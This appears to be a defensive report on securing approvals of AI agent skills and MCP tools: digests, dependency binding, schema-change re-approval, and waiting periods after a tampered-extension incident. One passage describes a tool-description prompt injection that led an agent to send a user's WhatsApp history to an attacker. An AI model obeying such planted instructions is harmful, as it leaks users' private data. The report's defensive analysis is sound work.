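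Standing approvals in Claude Code and Codex are weaker than any of the four because they match the text of a command and store nothing about the files. A rule that allows `python scripts/extract.py` still applies after somebody replaces the script. Since March 2026, OpenClaw has refused such a command unless the approval fixes exactly one local script, but this doesn't cover the packages the script imports.

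### Why agents disagree about the files

The agent seems a natural choice to produce the approval record, since it has usually read the project. Hossen tested this with Codex, using GPT-5.5 without reasoning, and Claude Code, using Claude Sonnet 4.6. In the main test, each agent had to decide which files a run depended on and calculate one digest over them. Of 62 records, 61 had a correctly calculated digest. Fifty-nine covered every file that Hossen had identified by hand, but only 24 of those included no other files.

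The agents did well with digests because an ordinary program can calculate them. Naming the files is harder because the agent has to work out how each tool finds its inputs and which files are relevant. In one case, the agents included a whole folder with documentation and examples, which is defensible because the deployment tool opens the folder itself. If the whole folder counts as correct, the number of exact records rises from 24 to 40.

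Other differences were dangerous. For one deployment with Terraform, a tool that creates cloud resources from text files, 16 runs produced five different sets of files. Two of Claude Code's records covered five workflow files but none of the 42 Terraform files, even though the accompanying summaries mentioned Terraform. The test folder lacked the file connecting the workflow to Terraform, which made the task harder, but Codex included all 42 Terraform files in every run. The two bad records looked as valid as the others, and a check against their digests would have accepted any change to the Terraform files.

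The agents could not reliably tell when one file was enough. When Hossen let them report that a single-file record was insufficient, they did so in 44 of the 48 runs where this was true, but also in 15 of the 16 where one file was sufficient. Newer models may do better. People found the task difficult too. Hossen prepared candidate sets for 30 projects but dropped seven because the audit could not complete them.

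Hossen concludes that the program enforcing the approval should calculate the digest itself. It can treat the agent's list of files as a suggestion, but it should take the actual list from something it can check, such as the deployment tool's own record of its inputs, a reviewed manifest or a rule that covers a whole folder.

For skills, the folder rule is the easiest. A list taken from SKILL.md would usually be incomplete. Of the 526 public skills with other files that Zhu and Wang examined, only 21 mentioned all those files by path. The folder rule can also miss files. In the same study, 67 of all 549 skills linked to files elsewhere in the repository, and a reviewer has to add any of those that the agent will use.

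### Changing one package in the invoice skill

Suppose the firm keeps its own copy of the invoice skill, with the lockfile in the skill's folder. It wants one digest that covers the skill and the packages installed for it. The following script adapts Hossen's method to two whole folders, which are the ones named in the Codex profile earlier:

```python
from hashlib import sha256
from pathlib import Path

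lines = []
for folder in ["~/skills/invoice-extraction", "~/venvs/invoices"]:
    root = Path(folder).expanduser()
    for path in root.rglob("*"):
        if path.is_file():
            name = folder + "/" + path.relative_to(root).as_posix()
            lines.append(name + "\0" + sha256(path.read_bytes()).hexdigest())

print(sha256("\n".join(sorted(lines)).encode()).hexdigest())
```

The script calculates a digest for each file, puts the file's name in front of it, sorts the lines and calculates a digest of the whole list. Because the list includes the names, moving or renaming a file changes the final digest. Sorting ensures that the order in which the computer lists the files doesn't affect it.

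When the firm approves the skill, it runs the digest script and stores the result, say `9b2c...`, in the approval record. Both folders are read-only under the Codex profile, so using the skill in that sandbox doesn't change the digest. The digest script has to run outside the skill's control, or a malicious skill could report the old value.

Pillow can change from version 12.4.0 to 12.5.0 without anyone editing `SKILL.md` or `extract.py`. Someone might generate a new lockfile and reinstall the packages from it. Or an employee might install another tool into the same environment, and pip might upgrade Pillow during that install without changing the lockfile.

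| What the firm compares | New lockfile | Upgrade that bypasses the lockfile |
|---|---|---|
| Version label, 1.3 | Misses it | Misses it |
| The author's signature on the original files | Misses it | Misses it |
| Digest of SKILL.md (single-object binding) | Misses it | Misses it |
| Commit in the firm's repository (commit binding) | Notices once someone commits the lockfile | Misses it |
| Digest of the lockfile (manifest binding), with package digests checked by pip | Notices | Misses it until the next installation |
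| Digest over the skill's folder | Notices | Misses it |
| Digest over the skill's folder and the installed packages | Notices | Notices |

The last line is the only one that catches the second kind of change before `extract.py` runs. It also raises the most alarms, since even a harmless update to any package changes the digest. Building a fresh environment from the lockfile for each run is a simpler alternative that prevents accidental upgrades, but it makes every run slower to start.

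Hossen defines the authority set as only the files in the repository, and says packages need their own controls, such as lockfiles. The last line of the table also treats the installed packages as part of what the firm approved. That is reasonable here because pdfplumber and Pillow run with the same permissions as `extract.py`.

### Binding permission to the whole dependency tree

A digest of two folders works for the invoice skill because everything it runs is in those folders. Other skills call further skills, outside services or packages that they download while running. Zhu and Wang designed ClosureBound for these cases. It ties a permission to everything the skill depends on, directly or indirectly, and checks all of it again immediately before an important action.

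Their example is a skill called `invoice-pay` that pays a supplier using a second skill, `bank-wire`. The user approves the payment with `bank-wire` 2.1, but that version is not pinned, and the agent later loads 2.2. The new version contacts an analytics service and changes the recipient. The files and signature of `invoice-pay` are unchanged, so checking them does not reveal the change in `bank-wire`.

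ClosureBound represents the dependencies as a graph. Its nodes include skills, files, packages, tools, models and services, and its edges record how one node uses another. The edges matter because a package that a skill calls through a sandboxed helper is less dangerous than the same package called directly. In simplified form, the system calculates

ρ = *H*(*root*, *nodes*, *edges*),

where *H* is a digest function and *root* identifies the skill that the user approved. Each node's entry contains its location, version and digest, among other details.

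The user's approval stores this value with a limit on what the skill may do, for example paying one supplier up to a certain amount. Before the payment goes out, ClosureBound rebuilds the graph and allows the payment only if the new ρ equals the stored one and the payment is within the limit. When `bank-wire` changes to 2.2, ρ changes too, so the system lists the differences and requests a new approval.

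The limit applies to the payment itself, however the agent requests it. An agent that isn't allowed to use the payment tool therefore can't get around the limit through the bank's website or a shell command, provided ClosureBound recognizes the payment there. If ClosureBound can't tell what a command will do, it blocks the command.

Zhu and Wang tested a small model of the system on 40 invented cases, of which 32 were unsafe. Checking only the main skill let through 26 of the unsafe cases. Checking the whole graph when the skill loaded, but not again before the action, let through 20, partly because that version also placed no limit on the action. The full design stopped all 32 and handled the eight harmless cases correctly. These results illustrate why each check is there, but they are weak evidence of performance in practice, since Zhu and Wang wrote the cases to exercise those checks.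 They have not tested the system with real package managers, MCP servers or agents.

The biggest practical problem is finding all the dependencies. ClosureBound's guarantees assume a complete graph, but none of the 549 public skills that Zhu and Wang examined declared its dependencies in its header. The system stops if a known dependency is unresolved, but it can't account for one that nobody has discovered. Even a remote service that is in the graph poses a risk, because its operator can change it undetected.

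Binding an approval to the whole dependency tree also means that any package update requires a new approval. A skill with 1,754 packages could need one almost every day if its packages were free to update, so this binding is practical only once a lockfile fixes their versions.

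## Which changes to an approved tool should need a new approval?

A sensible rule is to require a new approval when an update lets a tool do something nobody has approved. If a firm asks for approval after every change, its employees will soon click through the requests without reading them. But if it asks only when something stops working, it will miss updates that give a tool more power without breaking anything. Software can detect some of these updates by comparing the tool's old and new interface or permissions, but that comparison doesn't reveal changes in the code behind them.

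### How a tool definition changes after approval

When an agent connects to an MCP server, the client requests a list of tools and passes their definitions to the model. The server can return different definitions the next time the client asks. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (April 2025) described this weakness and named it the MCP rug pull. Some clients asked the user to approve a tool at installation, but a malicious server could rewrite the tool's description afterwards.

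A week later, Invariant Labs' *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrated the attack. The security company built a server with one tool, which returned a random fact. The second time the server started, the tool's description contained instructions about a different, trusted server that sent WhatsApp messages. The agent followed them and sent the user's chat history to the attacker's number, without calling the random-fact tool. A sandbox around the malicious server would not have helped, because the server only supplied text and the agent sent the chat history with a tool it was allowed to use. The code editor Cursor asked the user to confirm the message, but the dialog seemed to show only a short greeting unless the user scrolled sideways.

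PolicyLayer, a vendor, had found no named victim of a changed tool definition by April 2026, according to its reference page *MCP rug pull*. The known harm from updates has come from changed code, as with postmark-mcp.

The protocol still leaves each client's developer to detect such changes. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), which describes the version of 28 July 2026, a server's tool list may change over time, and a server that offers change notices should send them to subscribed clients. Clients should ask users to confirm sensitive operations and show them what a call will send. Clients must distrust a server's hints about its tools, such as a claim that a tool only reads data, unless they trust the server. But the document doesn't require a client to compare a new definition with the approved one or to ask for approval again.

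A hostile server can withhold the notice, so a client has to make the comparison itself each time it fetches the list. The same version of the Model Context Protocol lets servers suggest how long a client may keep a list before fetching it again. Servers may also show different tools to users with different authorization, so a client should store the approved definitions separately for each account.

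This question is open for the Model Context Protocol. The charter of its Security Interest Group includes deciding whether a change after approval is a versioning matter, a reason for re-approval or a security event.

### Signed definitions

In *ETDI*, Bhatt, Narajala and Habler (2025) proposed that providers sign each tool definition, including its version number and the permissions it needs. The client checks the signature and stores the version and a digest of the approved definition. It asks the user to approve the tool again if the version is newer, or if the content has changed under the same version number. Whether the client allows an older version depends on its policy.

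This would have exposed Invariant Labs' changed description. It works less well on Bhatt and colleagues' own example, in which a wallpaper tool starts to search the user's documents while its provider leaves the version at 1.0. They suggest including a digest of the server's interface specification in the definition, so that a change to the interface requires a new version. But the provider could add the search without changing the interface, and the signed definition would stay the same.

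ETDI has not become part of the Model Context Protocol, and none of the proposals the protocol had accepted by late November 2026 covers signed tool definitions. ETDI is available on PyPI as a separate package, *Model Context Protocol Python SDK with ETDI Security*, and developers turn the protection on for individual tools. *MCPS* (Sharif, 2026) makes a similar proposal in an Internet-Draft, a working document that anyone can submit to the internet's main standards body.

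Signing also doesn't change the number of approval requests. A client that requests approval for every new version treats a typo fix the same as a new ability to run programs.

### Compatible updates that widen authority

Software developers usually call an update backward compatible if everything that worked before still works. Ameur, Bouzefrane and Banerjee (2027) show in *SchemaCaps* that such an update can give an agent more authority than the user approved.

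Their main example is Desktop Commander, an MCP server that runs commands on the user's computer. In simplified form, one of its tools changed like this:

```
0.1.34   execute_command(command, timeout_ms)
0.1.35   execute_command(command, timeout_ms, shell)
```

The new version of the tool accepts an argument that the old one rejected, which lets the agent choose the shell, the program that interprets the command. Every old call still works, so the update is backward compatible. But a firm may have allowed only certain commands because it knew what they did in one shell. The same text can do something else in another shell, so the firm's rule no longer determines what can run.

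The two ideas are easy to compare in symbols. Let *S* be the old input schema, *S*′ the new one, and [*S*] the set of all calls that *S* accepts. An update is compatible if

[*S*] ⊆ [*S*′],

so that the new schema accepts every old call. Now let *K* be the arguments that carry authority, and let π<sub>*K*</sub> keep only the values of those arguments. The update is *non-amplifying* if

π<sub>*K*</sub>[*S*′] ⊆ π<sub>*K*</sub>[*S*].

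An update amplifies if it lets the agent give a protected argument, or a combination of them, values that were impossible before. If a call omits an argument, Ameur and colleagues use the default declared in the schema. If there is no default, they write ⊥, meaning that the server sets the value. For `shell`, the only possible value in version 0.1.34 was ⊥. In 0.1.35 it can be any string, so the update amplifies.

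An argument carries authority if it can change what the tool acts on, where data goes, whose account the tool uses or how something runs. For example, a web address for sending results carries authority, but a limit on the number of results doesn't. Because argument names can be misleading, SchemaCaps by default treats every argument as carrying authority until the client's owner marks it as harmless.

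Compatibility and authority can vary independently:

| Change to the schema | Do all old calls still work? | Can the agent do more? |
|---|---|---|
| A new optional argument, where the tool used to reject unknown ones | Yes | Yes |
| A wider range of values for an existing argument | Yes | Yes |
| A new required argument, where the tool used to reject unknown ones | No | Yes |
| An optional argument becomes required | No | No |

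A new optional argument can expose confidential data. If the operator of the remote service that checks suppliers' tax numbers added one for the full text of an invoice, old calls would still work, but the agent might start to fill it in. The firm would then be sending out prices and bank details it had meant to keep confidential.

### The re-approval rule

SchemaCaps runs in a proxy between the agent and the server. When a tool changes, the proxy goes through these checks:

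1. It suspends the tool if the server's identity has changed, meaning the command that starts it or the name it reports.
2. It suspends the tool if someone has newly marked one of its arguments as harmless.
3. It suspends the tool if the server no longer describes it as read-only, or now describes it as destructive or as reaching outside systems.
4. If the input schema is the same, it keeps the approval, even if the description has changed.
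5. It suspends the tool if the arguments in the old schema depend on one another or if part of that schema is missing.
6. It compares each remaining argument, leaving out those marked as harmless. It suspends the tool if an argument can take a new value, if the tool starts to accept undeclared arguments, or if a default changes.
7. If nothing in these checks has suspended the tool, it keeps the approval, applies it to the new schema and records the decision.

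The proxy hides a suspended tool from the model and refuses calls to it. The user can approve the new version, reject it or tighten the rules for its arguments.

The fifth check is needed because examining arguments one by one can miss a change. Suppose a tool requires either a document's number or its path, and an update drops that requirement. Either argument could already be omitted, but now both can be, and the server then chooses the document. SchemaCaps prompts the user instead of analysing such cases.

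Removing an argument can also widen authority. If a tool no longer has a required `folder` argument, the server decides which folder to use. In a test with 330 artificial changes that widened authority, an earlier version of SchemaCaps kept the existing approval for 27, mostly because it missed this effect. The corrected version caught all 330, and all 333 in a second test. However, in the first test it also required an unnecessary new approval for 123 of the 270 changes that did not widen authority.

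Ameur and colleagues also proved that a series of updates can't gradually widen a protected argument if every step meets the definition. The proof assumes that each comparison is correct, but the software that makes the comparisons has only been tested, not proved correct.

### How many questions each rule asks

For a pilot study, Ameur and colleagues installed 604 releases of 39 public MCP servers, published between January 2025 and September 2026, and compared the tools in successive releases. They found 1,197 changed input schemas. Of these, 580 were compatible with old calls, and 412 of those 580 allowed a new value for some argument.

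Most of the 412 were probably minor, since the count treats every argument as carrying authority. When the researchers judged the arguments by hand, they found at least 76 compatible changes that added or widened an argument with real authority. Such arguments included the web address to which the Firecrawl server sends results and the target project in a GitLab server. The figures don't give a general rate because the servers were popular or official ones rather than a random sample, and a few accounted for most of the important changes.

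The team then counted how often four rules would have asked for a new approval of an existing tool:

| Rule | Re-approvals | What it accepts without asking |
|---|---|---|
| Ask if anything in the definition changes | 2,004 | Changed behaviour behind an identical definition |
| Ask if the input schema changes | 1,197 | Changed behaviour behind an identical schema, and new descriptions |
| SchemaCaps | 645 | New descriptions, and changed behaviour if the schema stays the same or becomes narrower |
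| Ask if old calls might fail | 617 | New descriptions, changed behaviour behind an identical schema, and all 412 compatible widenings |

SchemaCaps produces only 28 more approval requests than the compatibility rule, and its requests are more useful. Most of the compatibility rule's requests are for changes that break old calls, which users would probably notice anyway.

SchemaCaps ignores tool descriptions, so it would have kept the approval in Invariant Labs' demonstration, where only the description changed. Ameur and colleagues exclude attacks through descriptions from its scope, but a firm can't ignore them, because the model reads descriptions as instructions. Microsoft (2026) advises reviewing changes to descriptions as strictly as changes to a system prompt.

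Of the 2,004 re-approvals under the strictest rule, 807 were for changes to descriptions or titles alone. A firm that used SchemaCaps and also reviewed every changed description would therefore have had at least about 1,450 changes to review. That is a much smaller reduction than with the 645 re-approvals under SchemaCaps alone, although comparing two short descriptions is usually quick.

### What clients did in September 2026

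Ameur and colleagues also examined eight clients, developer kits and scanners. They ran four against a test server that widened a file-reading tool during a session by removing a restriction on its reach and adding a web address as an argument. For the others, they relied on source code or documentation.

| Product | Evidence | Response to a wider input schema |
|---|---|---|
| MCP TypeScript SDK | Test | Sends calls that use the new argument |
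| MCP Python SDK | Test | Sends calls that use the new argument |
| Vercel AI SDK | Test | Accepts the change by default; an optional check reports any change |
| Visual Studio Code | Source code | Keeps the approval, which depends on the tool's name |
| Claude Code | Documentation | Loads the new list; permission rules match tool names |
| Claude Desktop | Documentation | Unknown |
| Cursor | Documentation | Unknown |
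| mcp-scan | Test | No warning, because it compares only descriptions |

None of the six products whose response is known asked for a new approval because a tool's authority had grown. Mcp-scan, originally from Invariant Labs, checked for changed descriptions up to version 0.4.5, but its developers removed that check in the next release. A firm that wants to check for either change may therefore have to add its own proxy or use Vercel's optional check.

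### Changed behaviour behind the same definition

A server can change what a tool does without changing the tool's definition. *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning* (Kim and Kang, 2026) reports examples from ordinary releases. Version 0.22.2 of DBHub, a database server, let a certain call change the database even in read-only mode. Version 0.22.6 blocked the same call. A firm that returned to the older version would lose this fix, and the tool definition would not show the difference.

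A change can also take effect between a user's approval and the action. If the agent gives only a name, GitHub's MCP server creates a private repository in version 1.4.0 but a public one in 1.3.0. If an administrator restores the older version while a call waits for approval, the user approves a private repository and gets a public one. In Kim and Kang's tests, stating `private: true` in the call prevented this. Agents should therefore state any setting that affects security, even when the current default is safe.

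*ProbeID* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) checks for changed behaviour by repeating test calls. When a firm approves a tool, ProbeID generates calls that fit the tool's input schema and stores the responses, leaving out parts that normally vary, such as timestamps. Later it picks some of these calls at random and sends them again. The random choice makes it hard for the server's operator to prepare honest answers for the test alone.

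If *f* is the current tool and *r* the recorded one, the average difference over *m* test calls is

*D* = (1/*m*) Σ *d*(*f*(*x*<sub>*i*</sub>), *r*(*x*<sub>*i*</sub>)),

where *d* is 0 for identical responses and at most 1 for different ones. If *D* is above a set threshold, ProbeID does not accept the tool.

In one experiment, ProbeID identified the original tool among eight impostors with the same description in 95.6% of cases. A simple check for identical responses did equally well, while methods that relied on descriptions did little better than guessing.

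Another experiment is closer to a rug pull, because the changed tool had replaced the original. For eight such tools, a check that required identical responses to 32 random calls missed the replacement 0.6% of the time, and with 64 calls it never did. The check always missed the changes in two other tools, because none of the stored calls triggered the changed behaviour. ProbeID accepted all the unchanged tools. When an agent used ProbeID on 16 tasks, the number of tasks affected by bad responses fell from 15 to 9.

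The number of test calls matters because a change may affect only some inputs. Suppose a change shows up in 5% of possible test calls and the firm investigates any difference. The chance that 32 random calls all miss it is about 0.95³², or 19%. With 64 calls, that chance falls to 4%. But if the tool misbehaves only for one customer's name, random calls will almost certainly miss the change.

Chen and colleagues also repeatedly tested 59 tools from 16 published MCP servers over eleven weeks. Seven tools changed their responses even though the server's version was pinned, three of them after the same versions were reinstalled. The changes aren't necessarily hostile, but they show that pinning a version doesn't guarantee the same behaviour.

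Test calls can't detect an action that leaves the response unchanged. ProbeID would have missed the hidden copies that postmark-mcp sent, as long as the server still reported that each email had gone out. If a tool was already malicious when the firm recorded its responses, later tests would only confirm that it still behaved the same way. A firm can safely repeat a database query as a test, but it would need a test account to repeat a payment or an email.

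### Approval fatigue

Approval fatigue is the tendency to accept requests without reading them after seeing too many. A March 2026 post on the Model Context Protocol blog reports that developers of autonomous agents see confirmations as friction and rely on sandboxes instead. It adds that most clients treat installing a server as the sign that the user trusts it.

Even SchemaCaps could cause this problem. Somebody who used all 39 servers in the pilot would have seen about 31 questions a month with it, and 95 under the strictest rule. The real numbers could be higher, because the study included at most 20 releases of each server. Ameur and colleagues warn that people may still approve without thinking when faced with 645 questions, and they have not tested how users respond.

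Approval requests would be much easier to judge if the client showed one per update, listing the new powers and the tools that receive them. One server in the pilot added the same two file-path arguments to 37 tools. A client that asked about each tool would show 37 nearly identical requests, and few people would read the last one as carefully as the first. An automatic labeller based on argument names flagged 84 compatible changes as important, and these came in only 20 updates.

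Using such a labeller to cut the questions further, from 645 to 413, is riskier because it found at most 60% of the arguments that people judged to carry authority.

The reviewer also needs to be shown any change in permissions, because it is hard to find in a whole package. Browsers have done this for extensions for years. If an update requests a new permission, the browser disables the extension until the user accepts the permission. *AgentRiskBOM* (Dutta and Moharir, 2026) extends the idea to a whole agent, using a record of the agent's tools, permissions, credentials, memory, approval requirements and logs, among other things. A program compares the record for a new version with the old one.

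Dutta and Moharir wrote records for 13 open-source agents and made 33 changes to them, such as adding a tool or removing an approval requirement. The program found and correctly classified all 33, but the test was easy because the changes were in the fields that the program compares. If a developer adds a capability without declaring it, the comparison will not show it. Wu, Li and Liu found that undeclared capabilities are common in skills.

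A new version can also do harm with the permissions the tool already has, as postmark-mcp did. Somebody therefore still has to read the changed code, though a list of changed permissions is a good way to decide how thorough the review should be.

### An invoice skill that asks for network access

Suppose the author of the invoice skill releases version 1.4, which converts foreign totals into the firm's own currency. The script now downloads exchange rates. The firm compares the permissions in its approval record with those the new version needs:

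```diff
 skill: invoice-extraction
-version: 1.3
+version: 1.4
 permissions:
   read: invoices/, the skill's folder, installed packages
   write: output/
-  network: none
+  network: rates.example
   secrets: none
```

Version 1.4 needs a new approval because it adds the first address the script is permitted to contact. Version 1.3 could already read bank details, and the update would also let the script send them out. A compatibility check would still pass, because the agent starts the script with the same command and old invoices produce the same table.

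The reviewer should first read every changed line and check what data the script sends. A request for exchange rates needs a currency and a date, but not supplier names or totals. Even if the reviewer finds no problems in this version, a later one could send more data to the same address without needing another permission.

The firm can avoid that risk by dividing the work between two scripts in separate sandboxes. The first downloads the rates into `rates/` and can't read the invoices. The second, `extract.py`, reads the rates and the invoices but has no network access. `extract.py` must not be able to write to any folder that the first script reads, or it could pass invoice data to that script. `extract.py` can then convert currencies with only one new permission, read access to `rates/`.

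Other updates to the skill call for different amounts of work:

| Update | New power | What the firm does |
|---|---|---|
| `extract.py` recognizes another invoice layout | None | A reviewer reads the changed lines |
| A new release of Pillow fixes a vulnerability | None expected | A reviewer checks the release and updates the lockfile |
| The skill no longer needs one of its folders | None; it needs less access | A reviewer reads the changed lines and tightens the sandbox |
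| `extract.py` also reads the firm's contracts | Access to more files | The IT and accounts departments decide again, after a full review |
| SKILL.md tells the agent to email the table | None for the script, but the agent now sends data out | The IT and accounts departments decide again, after a full review |

The firm records a new digest for every update. The first three updates don't need a new decision from the accounts department, because the sandbox still limits the script to what that department approved. A list of the script's permissions would not show the last update.

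An author may also leave the network access undeclared, by mistake or on purpose. The old sandbox policy would then block version 1.4 from downloading the rates. If the runtime prompts an employee to allow the connection, the request should go to the reviewer first, even if the employee wants the table quickly, because version 1.3 never had this access.

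## How quickly should updates be installed, and what follows a bad one?

A firm that waits before installing an update gives other people time to discover whether the release is malicious. But during the wait, attackers can exploit known security holes that the update would close.

Never updating isn't safe either, because agent runtimes have flaws too, and the fix is usually an update. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-48124* describes a flaw in Cursor versions before 3.0.0 that let the editor run hook commands from a project's settings file without the user's approval, which could let an agent escape the sandbox. A firm that stayed on an older version would have kept this flaw. The Plugin4Shell fixes for Claude Code and Codex also reached users as updates.

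Waiting a few days to install an update can add very little risk. In 2025, a flaw in Claude Code's editor extensions let malicious websites connect to them and potentially run commands, according to Datadog Security Labs' *CVE-2025-52882* (2025). Anthropic published its advisory on 23 June, but GitLab's advisory database dates the fix to 13 June. A firm that waited three days would have had the fix a week before the advisory, while one that updated only in response to advisories would have stayed vulnerable for at least ten days.

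Other fixes are more urgent. SecurityWeek reports that CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, gave federal agencies three days to patch CVE-2026-20253, which lets attackers run code without logging in. A three-day wait before every update could use up all of that time.

### The tampered Claude Code extension

On 29 October 2026, Cursor's marketplace delivered malicious copies of Anthropic's Claude Code extension, numbered 2.1.312 and 2.1.313. Anthropic had not made them. Attackers had put them directly into the cache from which the marketplace serves downloads, under the extension's real identifier. They were available for about 11 hours, from 2:27 am to 1:35 pm Pacific Time. *Cursor traces marketplace breach to stolen Fireworks AI credential* (Rojas, 2026) quotes Cursor's estimate that at most 5,000 users requested the affected versions. *Cursor : une clé volée chez Fireworks AI à l’origine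 d’une cyberattaque* (Le Monde Informatique, 2026) points out that this figure counts possible deliveries, not confirmed infections.

The intrusion started with Fireworks AI, a supplier Cursor used to train and run models. Cursor had given Fireworks a key to some shared storage, and Fireworks exposed it. The attackers used the key to copy records of old coding-agent sessions, then used credentials in some of those records to get into several of Cursor's internal tools. Cursor noticed, revoked the key and replaced the credentials it knew about. But according to TecnoAndroid's *Cursor violato*, the attackers already had another credential that let them publish to the marketplace.

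The security company Phorion was the first to notice suspicious activity on users' computers, according to *В расширение Claude Code для Cursor внедрили троян для удалённого доступа* (2026), an article on the Russian site iXBT. Phorion initially named the wrong marketplace, Open VSX, and only version 2.1.313. According to menow.fr's *Claude Code : deux versions piégées sur Cursor*, Phorion published its report on 30 October, then corrected the marketplace and added version 2.1.312 the next day. A firm that searched its computers using only the first report could have missed an infected one.

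The attackers had added their own code to the start of the extension's main file and left the rest intact. This code ran as soon as the editor loaded the extension, even if the developer never used Claude Code. According to Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor*, it then added the attackers' SSH key to the keys accepted for logging in to the developer's account, opened a tunnel through which they could connect back, and installed a program that restarted the tunnel after a reboot.

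The code also sent the attackers the names, but not the values, of up to 40 environment variables that appeared to hold passwords or access keys. The attackers could use the names to tell which computers were worth targeting.

That visit would have failed on most computers, because turning on the SSH service required administrator rights that the extension usually lacked. TecnoAndroid's *Claude Code, estensione falsa su Cursor installava backdoor SSH* describes errors in the malicious code that also interfered. But a Mac was open to the attackers if its owner had already enabled remote login. Nobody has published how many computers they could enter.

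Uninstalling the extension removed only its own files. The SSH key and the startup programs were elsewhere on the disk and remained even after updating to version 2.1.314, so the tunnel could keep running. Cursor told users to look for a key labelled `svc-telemetry`, disconnect affected computers from the network and consider rebuilding them. It also advised using a different, trusted machine to replace every credential that an affected computer could reach.

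Cursor removed the malicious versions and took the marketplace offline. It found no other tampered extensions, replaced its keys and rebuilt the marketplace before reopening it. It also got the hosting company to shut down the attackers' server, which stopped the tunnels even for users who hadn't heard about the attack. Later it moved its model traffic away from Fireworks and redeployed its production systems. Network Security Magazine's *Cursor Says Stolen Fireworks AI Key Led to Trojanized Claude Code Extension* reports that Cursor last detected malicious activity on 1 November, so removing the extension had not ended the intrusion.

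Microsoft published its own analysis of the code on 30 October. Mynavi News reports that Microsoft found no malicious copies in its extension marketplace or on npm, and that Anthropic had confirmed its systems were intact. Checking the publisher would not have protected Cursor's users, because the listing was Anthropic's.

### How long do malicious releases go unnoticed?

The time varies from seconds to months, and it depends heavily on where the release appears:

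| Malicious release | Where | How long it went unnoticed or stayed available |
|---|---|---|
| Imitation of a Solidity extension, 2025 | Microsoft's marketplace | A few seconds |
| LiteLLM 1.107.0, October 2026 | PyPI | 3 minutes |
| Two packages from the Paperclip attacker, 2026 | PyPI | Under 2 hours |
| Tampered Claude Code extension, October 2026 | Cursor's marketplace | About 11 hours |
| Cloned Paperclip skills, July 2026 | skills.sh | 3 weeks |
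| Imitation of Claude Code, 2025 | npm | At least 8 weeks |
| Imitation of the skill ponytail, July 2026 | skills.sh | Still listed after about 4 months |

The Solidity case shows how much the marketplace matters. According to Snyk's *Cursor IDE malware extension compromise in USD500K crypto heist*, Microsoft's team removed the extension seconds after publication. On Open VSX, the same extension reached 54,000 listed downloads. SC Media's *Fake Visual Studio Code extension for Cursor led to $500K theft* reports that one developer lost $500,000 in cryptocurrency after installing it. After Open VSX removed the extension, another malicious copy appeared there.

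A three-day wait would have been long enough for the first four cases in the table but not the last three. Those three were all imitations published under a new name or account, which a reviewer should catch by checking the source. MyBroadband's *Hackers try to hijack developers using Claude Code* (2025) reports that the imitation of Claude Code on npm had only 207 downloads when a security company identified it. Waiting is more useful against a bad release of a popular package, because more people are watching. These cases are not a random sample, and the table omits bad releases that nobody has discovered.

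One objection to waiting is that it works only if somebody else detects a bad update first. Phorion found the tampered extension through activity on users' computers. If all of Cursor's users had waited three days, Phorion would have had no such activity to notice, and they might all have installed the extension on the fourth day.

The objection is weaker where companies inspect new releases without waiting for a victim. AISLE, which found the malicious LiteLLM release, does this, though it has a commercial interest in advertising its speed. The Eclipse Foundation has announced scans of Open VSX with the same aim. Skill marketplaces are a harder case. Clubic's *De faux plugins pour Claude Code volent des mots de passe* reports that skills.sh was still offering the fake ponytail on 26 November, with three passed security audits.

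Attackers can also program harmful code to stay inactive until a typical waiting period has passed. A firm should therefore use the three days to make its own comparison of the new and old versions, at least for skills that few other people examine.

### Waiting periods in package managers

Several package managers can ignore releases that are younger than a chosen age. The settings are similar, but the units are not:

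| Package manager | Setting | Value for three days | Exception for an urgent fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| npm | `min-release-age` | `3` (days) | Override the setting for one command |
| pnpm | `minimumReleaseAge` | `4320` (minutes) | `minimumReleaseAgeExclude` |
| Yarn | `npmMinimalAgeGate` | `4320` (minutes) | `npmPreapprovedPackages` |
| Bun | `minimumReleaseAge` | `259200` (seconds) | `minimumReleaseAgeExcludes` |
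| uv | `exclude-newer` | `"3 days"` | `exclude-newer-package` |

pnpm counts the wait before installing a new release in minutes, so a `3` copied from npm's settings gives a wait of three minutes. pip's `--uploaded-prior-to` option sets a cut-off date for uploads.

For the invoice skill, the firm could put these lines in uv's configuration file:

```toml
exclude-newer = "3 days"
exclude-newer-package = { pillow = "2026-12-04T12:00:00Z" }
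```

The first line makes uv ignore any package file uploaded in the past three days. The second makes an exception for Pillow, allowing releases up to noon on 4 December, when a reviewer approved an urgent fix. A fixed time is safer than exempting Pillow altogether, because uv would still ignore a malicious release uploaded the next day.

Dependabot, GitHub's service for proposing dependency updates, makes the exception automatically. Its `cooldown` setting delays ordinary updates but not security updates. The exception applies only once an advisory exists, so a fix that a developer releases without one has to wait like any other update, which is a good reason to keep the wait short.

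These settings cover only packages, so they wouldn't have delayed the tampered Claude Code extension, which came through an editor's marketplace. For extensions, plugins and skills, the firm has to turn off automatic updates and install new versions itself when the wait is over. The Claude Code runtime has a "stable" release channel whose versions are typically about a week old. A firm on that channel needs to switch to the latest version when an urgent fix comes out.

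A waiting period also works only if the release date belongs to the file being installed. An attacker with access to a marketplace's cache, for example, might replace the file behind an old version number, and the new file would pass because of the old date. Only comparing the file's digest with the approved one would reveal the replacement.

### A three-day wait with one attack and one urgent fix

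Suppose two updates for the invoice skill's packages come out at 9 am on Monday. One is a malicious release of Pillow from a stolen account, which somebody discovers 11 hours later. The other is a version of pdfplumber that fixes a flaw attackers are already exploiting with specially made PDFs.

| The firm's rule | Malicious Pillow | Fix for pdfplumber |
|---|---|---|
| Install immediately | Runs on the firm's computer | In place on Monday at 9 am |
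| Wait three days, without exceptions | Gone 61 hours before the wait ends | In place on Thursday at 9 am |
| Wait three days, but review urgent fixes within four hours | Gone 61 hours before the wait ends | In place on Monday at 1 pm |

If the firm receives 20 invoices a day and follows the rule without exceptions, it will open about 60 PDFs with a library that attackers know how to exploit. The sandbox would limit the damage, but a successful attacker could still read the other invoices and alter the table. Under the last rule, the firm can stop using the skill until 1 pm, which would delay invoice processing by a few hours.

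Thoughtworks also recommends a fast route for urgent security patches, provided somebody verifies them. Verification matters because an attacker can label a malicious release an urgent fix. The reviewer should find the advisory somewhere other than the release itself, such as the CVE list or the developer's website, and check that the changed lines fix the flaw it describes. The wait can be shorter for these patches, but the reviewer should read the changes as thoroughly as for any other update.

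### Staged rollout and rollback

In a staged rollout, the firm installs an update on a few computers first and on the rest only if nothing goes wrong. A firm with 50 computers might install it on five and wait a day. If it had done this with the tampered extension, the other 45 would still have had the old version when Cursor withdrew the new one.

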